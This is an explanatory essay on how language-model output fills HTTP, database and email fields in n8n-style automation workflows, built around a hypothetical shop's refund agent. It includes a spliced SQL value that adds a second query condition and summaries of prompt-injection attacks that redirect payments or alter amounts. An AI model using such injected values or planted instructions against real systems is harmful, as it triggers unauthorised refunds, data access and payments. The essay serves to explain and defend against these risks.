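# Language model output as node parameters in low-code automation: how model-filled HTTP and database fields cause unintended actions

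## How a model's output becomes a node setting

Low-code automation platforms let people connect web services, databases and messaging accounts without writing a program. The builder of an automation places ready-made steps on a canvas, connects them and fills in a form for each one with details such as the address to call, the table to search or the recipient of an email. The platform runs the steps whenever a chosen event occurs. n8n, a platform that organisations can host on their own servers, now lets a large language model fill in parts of the form, as do several of its competitors. The model supplies a value such as a recipient, an order number or a search condition, and the step runs with that value under the organisation's stored login.

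The login makes this different from a chatbot. A person can ignore a chatbot's wrong answer, but a wrong value in one of these forms becomes a request that another company's server carries out, a changed database row, or an email in a customer's inbox. We call these effects outside the workflow "external actions", and we call any field value that comes from a model's output a "model-filled value".

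Tang, Zhou and Chen (2026), in *Characterizing Large Language Model Agentic Workflows*, collected 6,003 public n8n templates with at least one language-model component and counted 104,743 executable steps in them, about 17 per template. Generating text was the main task in 31% of the templates, extracting information in 18%, and planning or acting through tools in 17%. A DeepSeek model assigned these labels and matched the researchers' own in 192 of 200 cases. Templates are designs that people share, so the counts don't measure how often anyone runs them.

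### The parts of a workflow

A node is one step in a workflow, and the builder configures it through fields. In n8n, the *HTTP Request* node can call any web service and has fields for the method (GET, POST, DELETE and four others), URL, query parameters, headers and body. The *Postgres* node works on a PostgreSQL database and offers six operations, from selecting rows to deleting a whole table. A trigger is the node that starts the workflow when an event arrives, such as an email or a chat message.

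Nodes pass data to each other as a list of items, each a JSON object (JSON is a text format made of names and values). A node that receives several items performs its operation once for each. In n8n's example, a node that creates cards on the task board Trello receives two items and creates two cards. Similarly, an email node that receives three items sends three emails, even though the builder configured only one.

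Most field values change between runs, so builders write expressions in the fields. An expression is a formula between double braces that the platform evaluates when the workflow runs. If the recipient field of an email node contains `{{ $json.email }}`, the node takes the value named `email` from the current item. According to n8n's *Key concept glossary*, expressions run JavaScript and can also use data from other workflows and settings of the n8n installation.

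A credential is a stored key, token or password. According to n8n's *Node types*, n8n encrypts credentials in its database and gives only certain node types access to them. The builder selects a credential once in the node's settings, and the node attaches it to every request. The model normally never sees the credential and doesn't need to, because the node authenticates the request the same way whether a person or a model filled in the other fields.

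The AI Agent node brings the model in. It is a root node, to which the builder attaches sub-nodes: a chat model, optionally a memory for earlier messages, and tools. A tool here is usually an ordinary node, such as HTTP Request, Postgres or Gmail, that the model can call on. At least one is compulsory, according to n8n's *AI Agent*, and since version 1.82.0 every such node works as what n8n calls a Tools Agent. (n8n also has a newer product named simply "agents", which lives outside workflows. The word "agent" here always means the node.)

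An agent's connections to its tools differ from the connections between ordinary steps. Tang and colleagues had to separate the two when they turned templates into graphs. Ordinary connections show the order of execution, while those from an agent to its tools show how the builder has configured the agent. A diagram of the workflow therefore shows that an agent can call a refund service, but not whether or when it will.

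### A shop's support workflow

A hypothetical shop answers customer emails with a workflow of this kind. An email trigger starts an AI Agent node with three tools. The Postgres tool reads a table of 10,000 orders. The HTTP Request tool posts an order id and an amount to a refund service, and the Gmail tool sends replies. Customer 417 has two of these orders, number 8812 for 80 euros and number 8813 for 45 euros.

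The builder has fixed some of the fields and left others to the model:

| Tool | Fixed by the builder | Filled by the model |
|---|---|---|
| Postgres | operation (Select), table, credential | the customer number to search for |
| HTTP Request | method (POST), URL, credential | order id, amount |
| Gmail | operation (send), account | recipient, subject, text |

The builder decides which fields go in which column. n8n would accept a version of this workflow in which the model also fills in the URL.

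### Two routes from the model to the field

Model output can reach a field without an agent. Suppose the shop had put a plain model node after the email trigger, with an output parser that requires the answer in a given JSON format. The model node produces an item containing `"order_id": 8812` and `"amount": 80`. The next node is an HTTP Request node whose body fields contain `{{ $json.order_id }}` and `{{ $json.amount }}`. These expressions would be the same if the two numbers had come from a web form, so a colleague who opens the node later has to trace the connection back to find out that they came from a model.

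On this route, the builder decides that the refund node runs and where it comes in the sequence, and the model supplies only the values. Many workflows give the model slightly more control. Tang and colleagues describe a template that fetches new Gmail messages every 15 minutes and has a model sort them into categories such as High Priority, Inquiry and Finance/Billing. Each category has its own prompt for drafting a reply, and the workflow then applies a label and saves the draft. The model writes the text of the draft, and its choice of category also determines which branch of the workflow runs.

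The other route is the tool call, a structured request in which the model names a tool and gives values for its parameters. The platform then executes the request. The model's output also determines which tools run, in what order and how many times, within a limit on how often the model runs (10 times by default in n8n's *Tools Agent*). The builder uses the `$fromAI()` function to mark the fields that the model should fill.

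One field can combine both routes. On n8n's community forum, Biraj_Mainali, in *How can an agentic HTTP request tool let AI dynamically set the…*, asked how a model could supply the id at the end of a URL. The accepted answer was this:

`{{$json.BASE_URL}}/contacts/{{ $fromAI('contactId', 'The ID of the contact to retrieve') }}`

The start of the address comes from the previous node's data and the end from the model. In a second reply, a user advised against this design and suggested having an agent prepare a list of URLs and a separate HTTP Request node call each one, saying that an agent with too many responsibilities makes more mistakes. That claim rests on one user's experience, not a measurement, and under the alternative a model would still write the URLs, including the part that now comes from the previous node.

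### One tool call, step by step

The function takes up to four arguments, which n8n sets out in n8n's *Use AI for parameters*. Only the key is compulsory. It is a name of 1 to 64 characters made of letters, numbers, underscores and hyphens. The description is free text for the model. The type can be string, number, boolean or json, and n8n assumes string if the builder gives none. The last argument is a default value. In the shop's HTTP Request tool, the two body fields contain:

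`{{ $fromAI("order_id", "Number of the order to refund", "number") }}`

`{{ $fromAI("amount", "Amount to refund, in euros", "number") }}`

n8n searches all the fields of the node for such calls, however deeply nested, and builds a parameter schema from their arguments. A schema is a formal description of which values a tool takes and of what type. The platform sends it to the model together with the tool's name and description, the agent's instructions and the customer's email. For the refund tool it comes to roughly this (the exact wrapping differs between model providers):

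```json
{
  "name": "refund_order",
  "description": "Refunds an order through the refund service",
  "parameters": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "order_id": {
        "type": "number",
        "description": "Number of the order to refund"
      },
      "amount": {
        "type": "number",
        "description": "Amount to refund, in euros"
      }
    },
    "required": ["order_id", "amount"]
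  }
}
```

The URL, the method and the credential do not appear in it because the builder has already fixed them and the model does not need to supply them.

Now customer 417 writes that order 8812 arrived broken. The model first calls the Postgres tool with the customer number, and the two orders come back. It then calls the refund tool. The complete call, from the model's output to the answer of the refund service, looks like this:

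```json
{
  "tool_call": {
    "name": "refund_order",
    "arguments": { "order_id": 8812, "amount": 80 }
  },
  "request_from_the_node": {
    "method": "POST",
    "url": "https://refunds.example/v1/refunds",
    "headers": { "Authorization": "<key from the stored credential>" },
    "body": { "order_id": 8812, "amount": 80 }
  },
  "result_for_the_model": {
    "status": "refunded",
    "order_id": 8812,
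    "amount": 80
  }
}
```

The model writes only the first block. n8n compares the arguments with the schema and stops with an error if they don't fit. In a forum thread titled *“Received tool input did not match expected schema” when calling HTTP tool*, one participant resolved the error by switching to another OpenAI model, apparently without changing the rest of the workflow. If the arguments fit, n8n replaces each `$fromAI()` call with the value that has the same key and evaluates the rest of the field. The node then attaches its credential and sends the request. A builder can add human review, so that a person approves or denies the call before it is sent, but the shop has not done so.

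The refund service's response goes back into the model's context, the text from which the model generates its next output. By default, the HTTP Request node returns only the body of the response. When the node serves as a tool, it can also pass on only selected fields or cut the text off after a set number of characters. n8n recommends this option to lower costs and improve results. The model may then call the Gmail tool to confirm the refund, or it may write a final answer and end the run.

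The database returned the amount of 80 euros, the platform placed it in the context as text, and the model generated it again as an argument. The model copied it correctly in this case, but no part of the shop's workflow compares the amount in the tool call with the amount in the orders table, or checks that order 8812 belongs to the person who wrote the email. The schema requires only two numbers, so it would also accept order 8813 or an amount of 8000.

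### Hints, not references

A builder used to expressions will easily misread `$fromAI()`, because `{{ $json.order_id }}` and `{{ $fromAI("order_id") }}` look nearly the same in a field. The `$json` expression copies the value stored under that name. For `$fromAI()`, n8n says the key and the other arguments "aren't references to existing values" and describes them as hints for the model. If the key is `email`, the model searches its context, the other tools and the input data for an email address, and in a chat it may ask the user for one.

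If the shop's Gmail tool has `$fromAI("customer_email")` as its recipient, the key is only a hint and does not tie the field to the sender's address. An expression could copy that address exactly from the trigger. The model will probably produce the same address, since it is the obvious candidate, but it could also produce one that the customer mentions in the email, which would also fit the hint.

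Builders can hand a field to the model without typing the function. Every suitable field of a tool has a button for this. Pressing it overwrites whatever the builder had entered, and n8n then shows a message in the field that the model defines this parameter. Clicking the X in that box returns control to the builder but leaves the generated expression in place for editing. *feat: Hints for tools and agent* (michael-radency, 2025), a change to n8n's code, added a notice for tools with no model-filled fields, telling the builder to click the button next to a parameter to let AI set its value.

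The builder can use the function to fill all or part of a field. n8n's own example is an email subject, `Generated by AI: {{ $fromAI("subject") }}`, where the opening words are fixed and the model supplies the rest. The HTTP Request tool once had a setting named "Let Model Specify Entire Body". A participant in the forum thread about schema errors noticed that it was gone by version 1.90.1, and got the same effect by letting the model write all of the JSON in the body field.

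Older tutorials give a different rule for the HTTP Request tool. *Tools AI Agent node*, an earlier edition of n8n's documentation, ruled out `$fromAI()` for the Call n8n Workflow, Code and HTTP Request tools. The current page excludes only the Code tool and sub-nodes that are not tools. The rule probably changed because the HTTP Request tool did. n8n now describes the old standalone tool as legacy, and new workflows use the standard HTTP Request node instead. The old tool had its own placeholders for the model to complete. After Leandro_Espinoza reported trouble with them in *Error when ai completes placeholders with arrays inside http request tool*, another user in the thread was advised to move to the new version, where `$fromAI()` should work.

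Some users had trouble after the change. In *Using $fromAI in a HTTP Request tool*, Basile_Bernard (2025) put the same URL, with two model-filled ids, into a Telegram message and an HTTP Request tool on version 1.83.2. The ids appeared in the message, but the HTTP tool produced no data. Another user with the same problem got a suggested fix to work only after switching the agent from an older type to Tools Agent, so the fault may have been in the older agent type and not in the HTTP node. With the restriction gone, a model can fill in fields of the HTTP Request node, which can call any service with a web interface.

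### Splicing and binding

Once the model has returned a value, the platform can put it into a request or a query in two quite different ways. Splicing means inserting the value as text into a larger string, which some other program parses afterwards. The URL in Biraj_Mainali's thread is a case of it. So is this query, if the shop's builder writes it in the Postgres node:

`SELECT * FROM orders WHERE id = {{ $fromAI("order_id") }}`

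The value `8812` produces a query for one order. The schema also permits `8812 OR id = 8813`, because the builder left the type at its default of string, and that value produces a query with two conditions. Nothing in the query the database receives shows that the second condition was meant to be part of a value.

Binding means passing the value separately from the statement it belongs to, so that the value cannot change the statement:

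`SELECT * FROM orders WHERE id = $1`

The value goes into a separate field, Query Parameters, as `{{ [ $fromAI("order_id") ] }}`. The longer text from before would now be treated as a single order number, and the query would fail because no order has that number. *Queries*, from the documentation of node-postgres, a widely used programming library for PostgreSQL, explains that the library sends the query text to the server unaltered, along with the parameters, and the server substitutes them safely.

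n8n recommends binding in its Postgres documentation but doesn't enforce it, and the query field accepts both forms. When MayurVirkar, in *SQL Injections*, asked on the forum what protection n8n offers against hostile input, the answer was that it depends on how one builds the workflow: query parameters prevent the attack, while an expression placed directly in the query can let it through. MayurVirkar replied that the parameters had never worked for him. One can see why a builder in that position would go back to splicing.

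### Other platforms

Other platforms use the same design under different names. In Nodul's *AI Agent Node* (the page also calls the platform Latenode), the builder connects nodes to the underside of an agent and writes `{{fromAIAgent("parameter_name"; "description")}}` in the fields the model should fill. The format has no place for a type or a default, so any restriction on the value has to go in the description. The platform uses the node's title as the tool's name and takes the tool's description from a separate field, so retitling a node also changes the tool name the model receives.

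In Nodul's worked example, an agent inserts a city name into the address of a weather service. The user asks about Berlin, but the agent substitutes "London" and makes the request. This is surely a slip by the page's author, but it shows that the mechanism does little to catch such an error. The address with London in it is just as valid, and the service would return a correct forecast for the wrong city.

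Atomemo's *HTTP Request Tool Node* relies more on prose. It recommends listing the required parameters in the tool's description, with an example such as "SKU-123" for a product number, and the model extracts the value from the conversation. Atomemo also advises builders to keep the service's key in a configuration node rather than typing it into the header field. ToolJet, a platform for building internal business software, lets builders attach any workflow node to an agent as a tool, including database queries, web requests and JavaScript.

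## Which fields decide what happens

A builder can have the model fill in an email's subject line in the same way as an order number, but a wrong order number can do much more harm. A wrong subject line means a customer reads an odd heading on the shop's email, while a wrong order number makes the refund service refund an order that nobody complained about.

### Control plane and data plane

A router moves packets from one line to another. In *Software-Defined Networking (SDN)*, Haleplidis, Pentikousis and colleagues (2015) assign the choice of line for each packet to the control plane, which sets up forwarding tables. The data plane forwards, drops or changes packets according to those tables. The idea of separating the two planes is older than the modern internet router and came up in work on telephone signalling.

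The telephone network shows why engineers wanted to separate data from commands. In the 1960s, AT&T's network carried voices and switching commands on the same path, so anyone who played a 2,600 Hz tone into a pay phone could call for free (Schneier on Security, *LLMs’ Data-Control Path Insecurity*, 2024). In the 1980s, Signaling System 7 moved the commands to a separate channel, and the tone stopped working. The essay attributes the same weakness to SQL injection and to prompt injection, in which text that a model should only process makes it follow someone else's instructions. Austria's computer emergency team, CERT.at (2025), likewise traces many security problems to data that a machine misinterprets as code.

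A workflow node shows control-plane and data-plane fields in the same form. A field belongs to the control plane to the degree that changing only its value changes the operation, its target, its scope or its recipient. It belongs to the data plane if changing it affects only the content of a message or record. A router handles the two planes with separate machinery, but a model may fill both kinds of field in one tool call.

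Ameur, Mendes and Bouzefrane (2026) use almost the same test in *Intent-Conditioned Argument Mediation for Tool-Using LLM Agents*. They call an argument "authority-bearing" if changing its value can change the call's principal (the party on whose behalf it runs), its recipient, its resource or the authority it runs with.

### Sorting the fields

Applied to the nodes in the shop's workflow, the test gives this order:

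| Kind of field | Examples | What a different value could do |
|---|---|---|
| Operation | HTTP method, database operation | delete an order instead of reading it |
| Target | host, path, table, record id, recipient | refund order 8813 instead of 8812 |
| Scope | filter, limit | change every order from March instead of one |
| Amount | sum of money, quantity | refund 8,000 euros instead of 80 |
| Content | subject, message text, note | tell the same customer something else |

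A field's name is only a rough guide to whether it decides what happens. If the builder sets the operation of n8n's Postgres node to Execute Query, that setting stays fixed, but the query text determines what the node does to the database. A model that fills in the query can therefore write either a `SELECT` or a `DELETE`.

Researchers disagree about how to classify an SQL query. Ameur and colleagues call it a selector, meaning that it picks out objects. Fan, Li and colleagues (2026), in *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security*, sort arguments into six roles (target, command, credential, content, selector and control) and put executable queries under command. Both classifications make sense, since a query names an operation and also picks out rows. Fan and colleagues add that an argument called `query` may be content in one tool, a selector in another and close to a command in a third.

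This makes automatic sorting of fields unreliable. Ameur and colleagues tried to infer the roles of 150 arguments from six third-party connectors and missed about a quarter of the authority-bearing ones. A builder who knows what the receiving service does with a field can do better by asking what a different value would change.

Some builders let the model choose which table to write to. In *Insert or update data in Postgres by AI agent*, a thread on n8n's forum, a user let the model fill in the Table field of a Postgres tool, and the model returned "employees". The insert failed because the call contained the settings but not the data to store. In a working version, a different value in that field would have sent the data to a different table.

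### Reachable actions

How much control the builder has given the model depends on both the kind of field and the set of actions that the open fields allow. An order id is a target whether the model can pick from two orders or ten thousand, but ten thousand orders allow many more actions.

*ToFu (2026)*, a study of the boundary between models and their tools, writes a tool call as C = ⟨T, {a₁ = v₁, …, aₙ = vₙ}⟩, a tool T with a value v for each argument a. In a workflow the builder has already fixed some of these values. Let c stand for everything fixed, including the tool and the credential, and let Vᵢ be the set of values that the i-th model-filled field accepts. The reachable actions of the node are then

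R = { act(c, v₁, …, vₖ) : v₁ ∈ V₁, …, vₖ ∈ Vₖ }

where act(c, v₁, …, vₖ) is the external action that follows when the node runs with those values. R therefore contains every action that the node could carry out as the model-filled values vary and everything else stays the same.

Taken literally, the definition would mean that a Gmail tool with a fixed recipient and a free body reaches far more actions than a refund tool with a free order id, because an email body accepts practically any text. The counts below avoid this by treating actions that differ only in content as the same action. They also leave out values that have no effect, such as an order number that doesn't exist.

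Suppose the shop adds a Postgres tool that marks orders as cancelled:

| What the builder leaves to the model | What one call can reach |
|---|---|
| nothing, order id fixed at 8812 | 1 order |
| a choice between customer 417's two orders | 2 orders, one at a time |
| any order id | 10,000 orders, one at a time |
| the filter that selects the orders | any group of orders, 2^10,000 − 1 possible groups |
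| the whole SQL statement | every statement that the database role permits |

The filter produces such a large number because each of the 10,000 orders can be in the group or outside it. With a free statement, counting orders no longer makes sense, since the statement can also change prices or touch other tables. The only limit left is the database role, which is the account n8n logs in with and its permissions. If the role can only read, a free statement can't cancel any orders, but it can still return all 10,000 to the model, along with the contents of any other table the role can read.

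When a tool has several open fields, the number of possible actions is the product of the number of values each field can take. In the shop's refund tool, the order id and the amount are both open. If the refund service accepted any amount from one cent to 1,000 euros, there would be 100,000 possible amounts for each of 10,000 orders, or a billion different refunds. If the service looked up the amount itself, there would be 10,000 possible refunds, one for each order.

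*Intent-Governed Tool Authorization for AI Agents (2026)* aims to minimize a similar quantity, the number of exposed effects, while keeping usefulness above a chosen threshold. Its system only approximates this goal, using broad classes of effects and limits on resources, which seems sensible because the exact counts grow so quickly.

The count of reachable actions shows what a single wrong value could do, but not how often wrong values occur. If customer 417 complains about order 8812, the model will nearly always return 8812, whether the field allows one order or 10,000. The count also covers only one call, and an agent may make several in a run.

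### Choosing a tool and filling it in

In a tool call, an agent can choose the wrong tool, or choose the right tool and fill in the wrong values. *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents (2026)* describes two attacks on a banking assistant that show this. In one, the user wants to move a refund into a savings account, and planted text makes the agent pay a bill instead. In the other, the user wants to send a colleague half the cost of a team dinner, and a planted "correction" gives a false total. The agent picks the right tool and recipient but transfers the wrong amount.

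*Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection? (2026)* builds on a benchmark in which eleven models often picked tools with more permission than the task needed, especially after a failure. Labelling each tool with its privilege reduced premature choices of this kind in every model that made them at a measurable rate. Such labels can help a model choose a narrow tool over a broad one, but they don't help it fill in the correct order ID once it has chosen the refund tool.

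A workflow in which the model chooses no tool can have more possible outcomes than an agent with several tools. For example, an agent might have three tools with no model-filled fields: one refunds order 8812 in full, one refunds order 8813 in full, and one forwards the email to an employee. Each call then has three possible outcomes. In a workflow without an agent, the refund node might always run and take only the order id from a model's output. That node can refund any of 10,000 orders. If the model also fills in the URL, the request can go to any address the node can reach.

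The number of tools attached to an agent is therefore a poor measure of what it can do. *How are AI agents used? (2026)*, a study of 177,000 tools built for the Model Context Protocol (a standard for connecting models to tools), finds that general-purpose action tools expand an agent's range of actions the most, while narrow ones expand it only somewhat. n8n's HTTP Request node is a narrow tool when its URL is fixed and the model fills in only one number, but it is about as general as a tool can be when the model fills in the URL, method and body.

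A single value can also change how severe a call is. *Beyond Attack-Success Rate (2026)* rates harmful actions by tool and, for some tools, by argument. It rates adding a participant to a calendar event as 2 on its scale if everyone is internal and 4 if the participant is external.

### Hard cases

Ameur and colleagues class an email subject as content. They built a program that checks each proposed tool call before it runs and tested it on 200 synthetic attacks. It blocked all 134 attacks on authority-bearing arguments and all 34 on SQL queries, but let through 24 of the 32 on content and payload fields, including all eight on email subjects. This difference is partly due to the design, because the program deliberately accepts text from documents in content fields. The results still show that a field in the data plane can do harm without redirecting the action, for example when a phishing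 message reaches a legitimate recipient.

An email's subject line can also trigger actions when software reads it. If the recipient is a helpdesk that closes every ticket with "resolved" in the subject, a model that writes that word there will close the ticket. The Gmail node's settings would not show the helpdesk's rule.

The refund amount is harder to classify, but it is better treated as a form of scope, because it sets how much of the shop's money the operation pays out, much as a filter sets how many rows a query affects. A strict reading of the test would make it data, since changing it from 80 to 8,000 leaves the operation, the order and the recipient the same.

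Designers of security policies have not settled on which fields must come from a trusted source either. In its rules for banking tools, *The LLMbda Calculus (2026)* requires a trusted source for the amount of a scheduled payment. For an immediate transfer, the recipient must be trusted, but the amount need only be information the recipient may read. This rule for the amount protects confidentiality but would not stop an inflated refund to the right customer.

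A free-text note can be data for the node that writes it but act as control once another workflow reads it. Suppose the shop's agent writes "customer wants money back" into a notes column. The first node only stores this text. If a second workflow passes new notes to a model with a refund tool, the note helps determine whether the model issues a refund. A builder who looks only at the first node will miss this.

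Values extracted from a document can both record facts about it and determine what a workflow does next. Tang and colleagues describe an invoice template in which a model extracts the vendor and the amounts, and later steps use these values to choose a branch and update a database.

### Why the value determines the action

The case for worrying about model-filled values rests on a short argument:

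1. When a node runs, it carries out the operation that its field values describe.
2. The builder has fixed some of those values, and the remaining ones settle which reachable action takes place.
3. The model's output supplies the remaining values, and nothing changes or rejects them before the action.
4. So whatever determines the model's output determines which of the reachable actions takes place.

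The builder still has a good deal of power, because the builder determines which actions are possible. For example, a model that fills in only the text of a reply to a fixed address determines very little of what happens.

The argument can also fail. The refund service may reject an 8,000-euro refund on an 80-euro order, so the node sends the request but no money moves. A rule or a person may also stop the call before the node sends it. The shop has neither, so whether the argument holds for its workflow depends on the refund service's own checks, which the builder may not know.

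The argument doesn't depend on an attacker. Ameur and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to send a summary to their manager, but the agent takes the legal team's address from the company directory. The summary goes to the wrong people even though the directory is genuine and nobody has planted anything. Outsiders can also influence the model's output, because customers write some of the text it reads.

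### If all data influences behaviour

One might object that the distinction is meaningless because all data influences behaviour. The wording of an email affects what the customer does next, and the length of a note affects how much storage the database uses. The objection is stronger for language models. Schneier on Security points out that a language model, unlike the telephone network, has no way to separate data from commands, and that people want data to affect how the model works.

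This is a fair description of the inside of a model, but the node's fields are separate. Text in the Gmail tool's body field cannot alter the recipient field of that call, however persuasive it is. Fan and colleagues use the example of a user who wants a web page summarised and emailed to their boss. The page should determine the body but not the recipient. To tell an attack from normal use, we have to ask which field the page influenced, because the page influences the call in both cases.

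Fan and colleagues tested whether the distinction matters by removing the roles from their own security system, which checks the source of each argument against its role. Without the roles, the system allowed 40% of legitimate tasks in a controlled test, down from 100%, and was no more secure. However, they had designed their scenarios around this distinction, so a large effect is unsurprising.

The results on AgentDojo, a general benchmark of agent tasks, are much less dramatic. Requiring every argument to come from a source as trusted as the user stopped all attacks and completed 14.4% of legitimate tasks. With roles, the system completed 18.6% of legitimate tasks and stopped 96.3% of attacks, which amounts to four more of the 97 tasks completed and one of the 27 attacks missed. The web page example supports the distinction better than these figures do.

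The objection that there is no sharp line between the planes is correct. A field can belong partly to each plane, or change planes when another program starts to read it, as the amount and the note show. A builder can still rank fields by how much they affect what happens, placing an order id above a greeting.

### A different problem from flaws in the platform

n8n has also had security flaws of the ordinary kind, and it would be easy to confuse them with this problem because both involve values in fields. GitHub's *GHSA-V98V-FF95-F3CP* (2025) describes a critical one in the part of n8n that evaluates expressions. A person with an account could write an expression while configuring a workflow, and under certain conditions n8n evaluated it without isolating it sufficiently from the underlying system. An attacker could use this to run any code with the privileges of the n8n process, and so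 read data, alter workflows or carry out operations on the server itself.

According to *CVE-2025-68613*, the flaw's entry in the US government's National Vulnerability Database (NVD), it affects versions from 0.211.0 onwards, and n8n fixed it in 1.120.4, 1.121.1 and 1.122.0. On 11 March 2026 the US cybersecurity agency CISA added it to its catalogue of vulnerabilities that attackers are known to have exploited.

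That attack needs an account on the n8n installation and a defect in n8n's code. Customer 417 has no account and edits no workflow. If the model returns order number 8813 instead of 8812, n8n works as designed, and the refund service receives a valid request for the wrong order.

The possible damage also differs, because code that runs as the n8n process can act far beyond any one node, while a wrong order id can only trigger actions available to the refund tool. Upgrading n8n removes the flaw in the expression evaluator but does not change what the refund tool can do. The advisory's temporary advice, to let only fully trusted users create and edit workflows, would not help the shop either, because a trusted employee built the refund tool and let the model fill in the order id.

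## Wrong, missing and malformed values without an attacker

A model can fill in a wrong value even when everyone is honest and all the software works as designed. Suppose customer 417 writes that a lamp arrived broken but forgets to give the order number. The refund tool requires one, so the model has to find a number, guess one, or use the Gmail tool to ask the customer instead.

Models often guess missing values. *Beyond the Leaderboard* (2026), an overview of agent failures, describes a 2024 experiment in which models tended to make up plausible values for missing parameters instead of asking for them. *Benchmarking LLM Tool-Use in the Wild* (Yu, Liu and colleagues, 2026) reports similar behavior in models released up to mid-2025, which frequently called a function when they should have asked a question first. On tasks that required a question, Gemini 2.0 Thinking did best among the leading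 models, with 52% right, while GPT-5 got 32% right.

### Values that look right

How much harm an invented order number does depends partly on how the shop numbers its orders. If its 10,000 orders have the numbers 1 to 10,000, every four-digit number belongs to a real order. Suppose the model swaps two digits of 8812:

`{ "order_id": 8821, "amount": 80 }`

The refund service finds order 8821 and pays 80 euros to a stranger. If the shop used random twelve-digit order numbers, an invented number would match a real order only about once in a hundred million tries, so the service would almost always return a "not found" error.

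Longer numbers don't help if the model picks the wrong one of two real orders. Customer 417 asks for a refund on "my last order", meaning 8812, and the database returns both orders. The model then makes this call:

`{ "order_id": 8813, "amount": 45 }`

Order 8813 exists, cost 45 euros, and belongs to the customer who wrote the email. Comparing the call with the orders table would find no error, because the model's mistake was in reading the email. If the model had mixed the two rows and requested 80 euros on order 8813, the comparison would have caught the error.

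The amount is a bare number, so the model and the refund service can interpret it in different units. If the service counts in cents, `"amount": 80` pays the customer 80 cents instead of 80 euros. If the service counts in euros but the model converts to cents, `"amount": 8000` requests 8,000 euros. Many services would reject a refund larger than the original payment, but 80 cents would pass that check, so a refund that is too small is more likely to go through. Currencies can also be confused. If a customer mentions having paid 93 dollars, the model may enter 93 without converting it, even though the field's description asks for euros.

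### Missing and empty values

A default value can hide the fact that the model gave no value at all. Suppose the builder tested the refund tool with order 8812 and left its price in the field as the default:

`{{ $fromAI("amount", "Amount to refund, in euros", "number", 80) }}`

Some weeks later the model calls the tool with `{ "order_id": 8813 }` and no amount. The node fills in the default of 80 and refunds the customer 80 euros on a 45-euro order. Without the default, the call would have failed because a required value was missing.

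n8n illustrates defaults with a field for the number of items in stock, which has a default of 5. If a node writes that value to an inventory table, the table will show five items that nobody has counted. A default is much safer where it can't be mistaken for a fact, such as "Hello" for a greeting.

Empty values are harder to predict, because each receiving program treats them in its own way. If the customer number is a string field, the model can call the Postgres tool with `{ "customer_id": "" }`. The search finds no orders, and the agent may then write to customer 417 that the shop has no record of any purchase. (In a deletion, an empty filter can match every row.)

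In a workflow without an agent, a node setting can let a missing value reach later nodes. Tang and colleagues counted 1,575 nodes in their n8n templates that the builder had set to produce output even when they would normally produce none. Suppose the shop looks up an order with such a node and finds nothing. The refund node still receives an item, but `{{ $json.amount }}` has no value. A strict refund service would reject the request, but one that treats a missing amount as a request for a full refund would pay out the full amount.

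### Objects, lists and loud failures

Sometimes the model has the right information but sends it in the wrong form. The refund tool needs a single order number, and the model might send a list or an object:

`{ "order_id": [8812, 8813], "amount": 80 }`

`{ "order_id": { "value": 8812 }, "amount": 80 }`

n8n rejects both calls because the builder gave the field the type number. If the type were json, both would pass, and the refund service would have to decide what to do with them. A service that accepts lists might refund both orders.

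In the n8n forum thread *Received tool input did not match expected schema*, an agent wrote a search request that worked when the user sent it directly to the search service, but n8n rejected it. Another participant traced the same error in their own workflow to the field's type. The button that lets the model fill in a field had set the type to string, but the model was sending a JSON object. When the participant changed the type to json, n8n changed it back to string. Writing the `$fromAI()` expression by hand, with json as its type, solved the problem.

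In *HTTP Request JSON variable $fromAI*, a user wanted an agent to register a device on a network by its MAC address, the hardware number that identifies the device. The service received `[{"value": "AA:AA:AA:AA:AA:AA"}]` instead of the address alone and returned an error. The user had typed `$fromAI(value)` into the body as plain text, and a reply explained that the function belongs inside an expression. (The reply's own example puts "string" where n8n expects a description. This does no harm, since string is the default type anyway.)

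Both failures are loud, meaning the run stops or an error appears somewhere. The builders lost time, but no device got onto the network by mistake. In a silent failure, the service accepts the wrong value and acts on it, as with the refund for order 8813.

How noticeable a failure is depends on what the receiving field accepts and has little to do with how wrong the value is. In the first thread n8n rejected a correct request, and in the shop the refund service carries out a wrong one. The request in the MAC address thread also had a description field containing the text "APITEST1". If the malformed object had ended up there, the service would probably have stored it without returning an error.

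*Closed-World Resolution Against Tool Hallucination in LLM Agents* (2026) sorts errors by where a program could detect them. With a list of the available tools and their schemas, a program can catch an invented tool name, a missing or undeclared argument, or a value of the wrong type. It can't use that list to catch the error when the model confuses two tools and the arguments fit both. It also can't catch the error when the model confuses order 8812 with order 8813, because both numbers fit the schema.

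A builder can also configure a node so that its failure goes unnoticed. Tang and colleagues found 2,608 nodes set to let the workflow continue after an error or to send the error down a separate branch, but only 111 nodes that deliberately stop the run with an error. Suppose the shop's workflow runs a refund node followed directly by a Gmail node, and the refund node is set to continue after errors. If the service rejects the refund, the workflow moves on anyway, and customer 417 gets an email saying that the money is on its way.

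### The same refund twice

A call with correct values can still do damage if it runs twice. Suppose the node sends a request to refund 80 euros for order 8812. The service pays, but the connection drops before its response arrives. n8n gets only a timeout, as it could if the service had never received the request.

If the builder has switched on the node's retry setting, n8n sends the request again and the customer gets another 80 euros. Tang and colleagues counted 1,854 nodes with retry settings in their templates. Each repeated payment request moves more money, but retrying the Postgres tool is harmless because searching for orders changes nothing. Marking an order as cancelled twice is also harmless.

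The agent can also repeat the call if the tool reports a timeout, because the model may reasonably treat the refund as failed. These repeats multiply the node's own retries. If the node makes up to three attempts per call and the agent calls the tool twice, the service may receive six requests and refund 480 euros for an 80-euro lamp.

An idempotency key prevents this, provided that the service supports it. The key is an identifier that the workflow sends along with the request, and it stays the same when the workflow repeats the request. The service stores the key together with the payment. When the same key arrives again, it returns the earlier answer without paying. The shop could build the key from the id of the incoming email and the order number:

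| Request | Key | What the refund service does |
|---|---|---|
| Refund 80 euros for order 8812 | `email-5521-order-8812` | pays and stores the key, but its answer gets lost |
| The same request again | `email-5521-order-8812` | finds the key and returns the first answer without paying |
| Refund 45 euros for order 8813 | `email-5521-order-8813` | pays, because the key is new |

The email id has to come from the trigger through an expression. If the model invented a key for each call, a repeated call would probably have a new key, and the service would pay again. A random key that the node generates on each attempt would fail for the same reason.

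The last row of the table shows that a key doesn't protect against a wrong value. If the agent should have refunded only order 8812, the service still treats the request for 8813 as a new refund. The key in this example also doesn't prevent a repeat refund after a second email. If customer 417 writes the next day to ask where the money is, the new email has a new id, and so a new key, and the agent could refund order 8812 again. A key made from the order number alone would stop that, but it would also block a legitimate second partial refund, so the shop has to decide which it needs more.

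### How often models give wrong arguments

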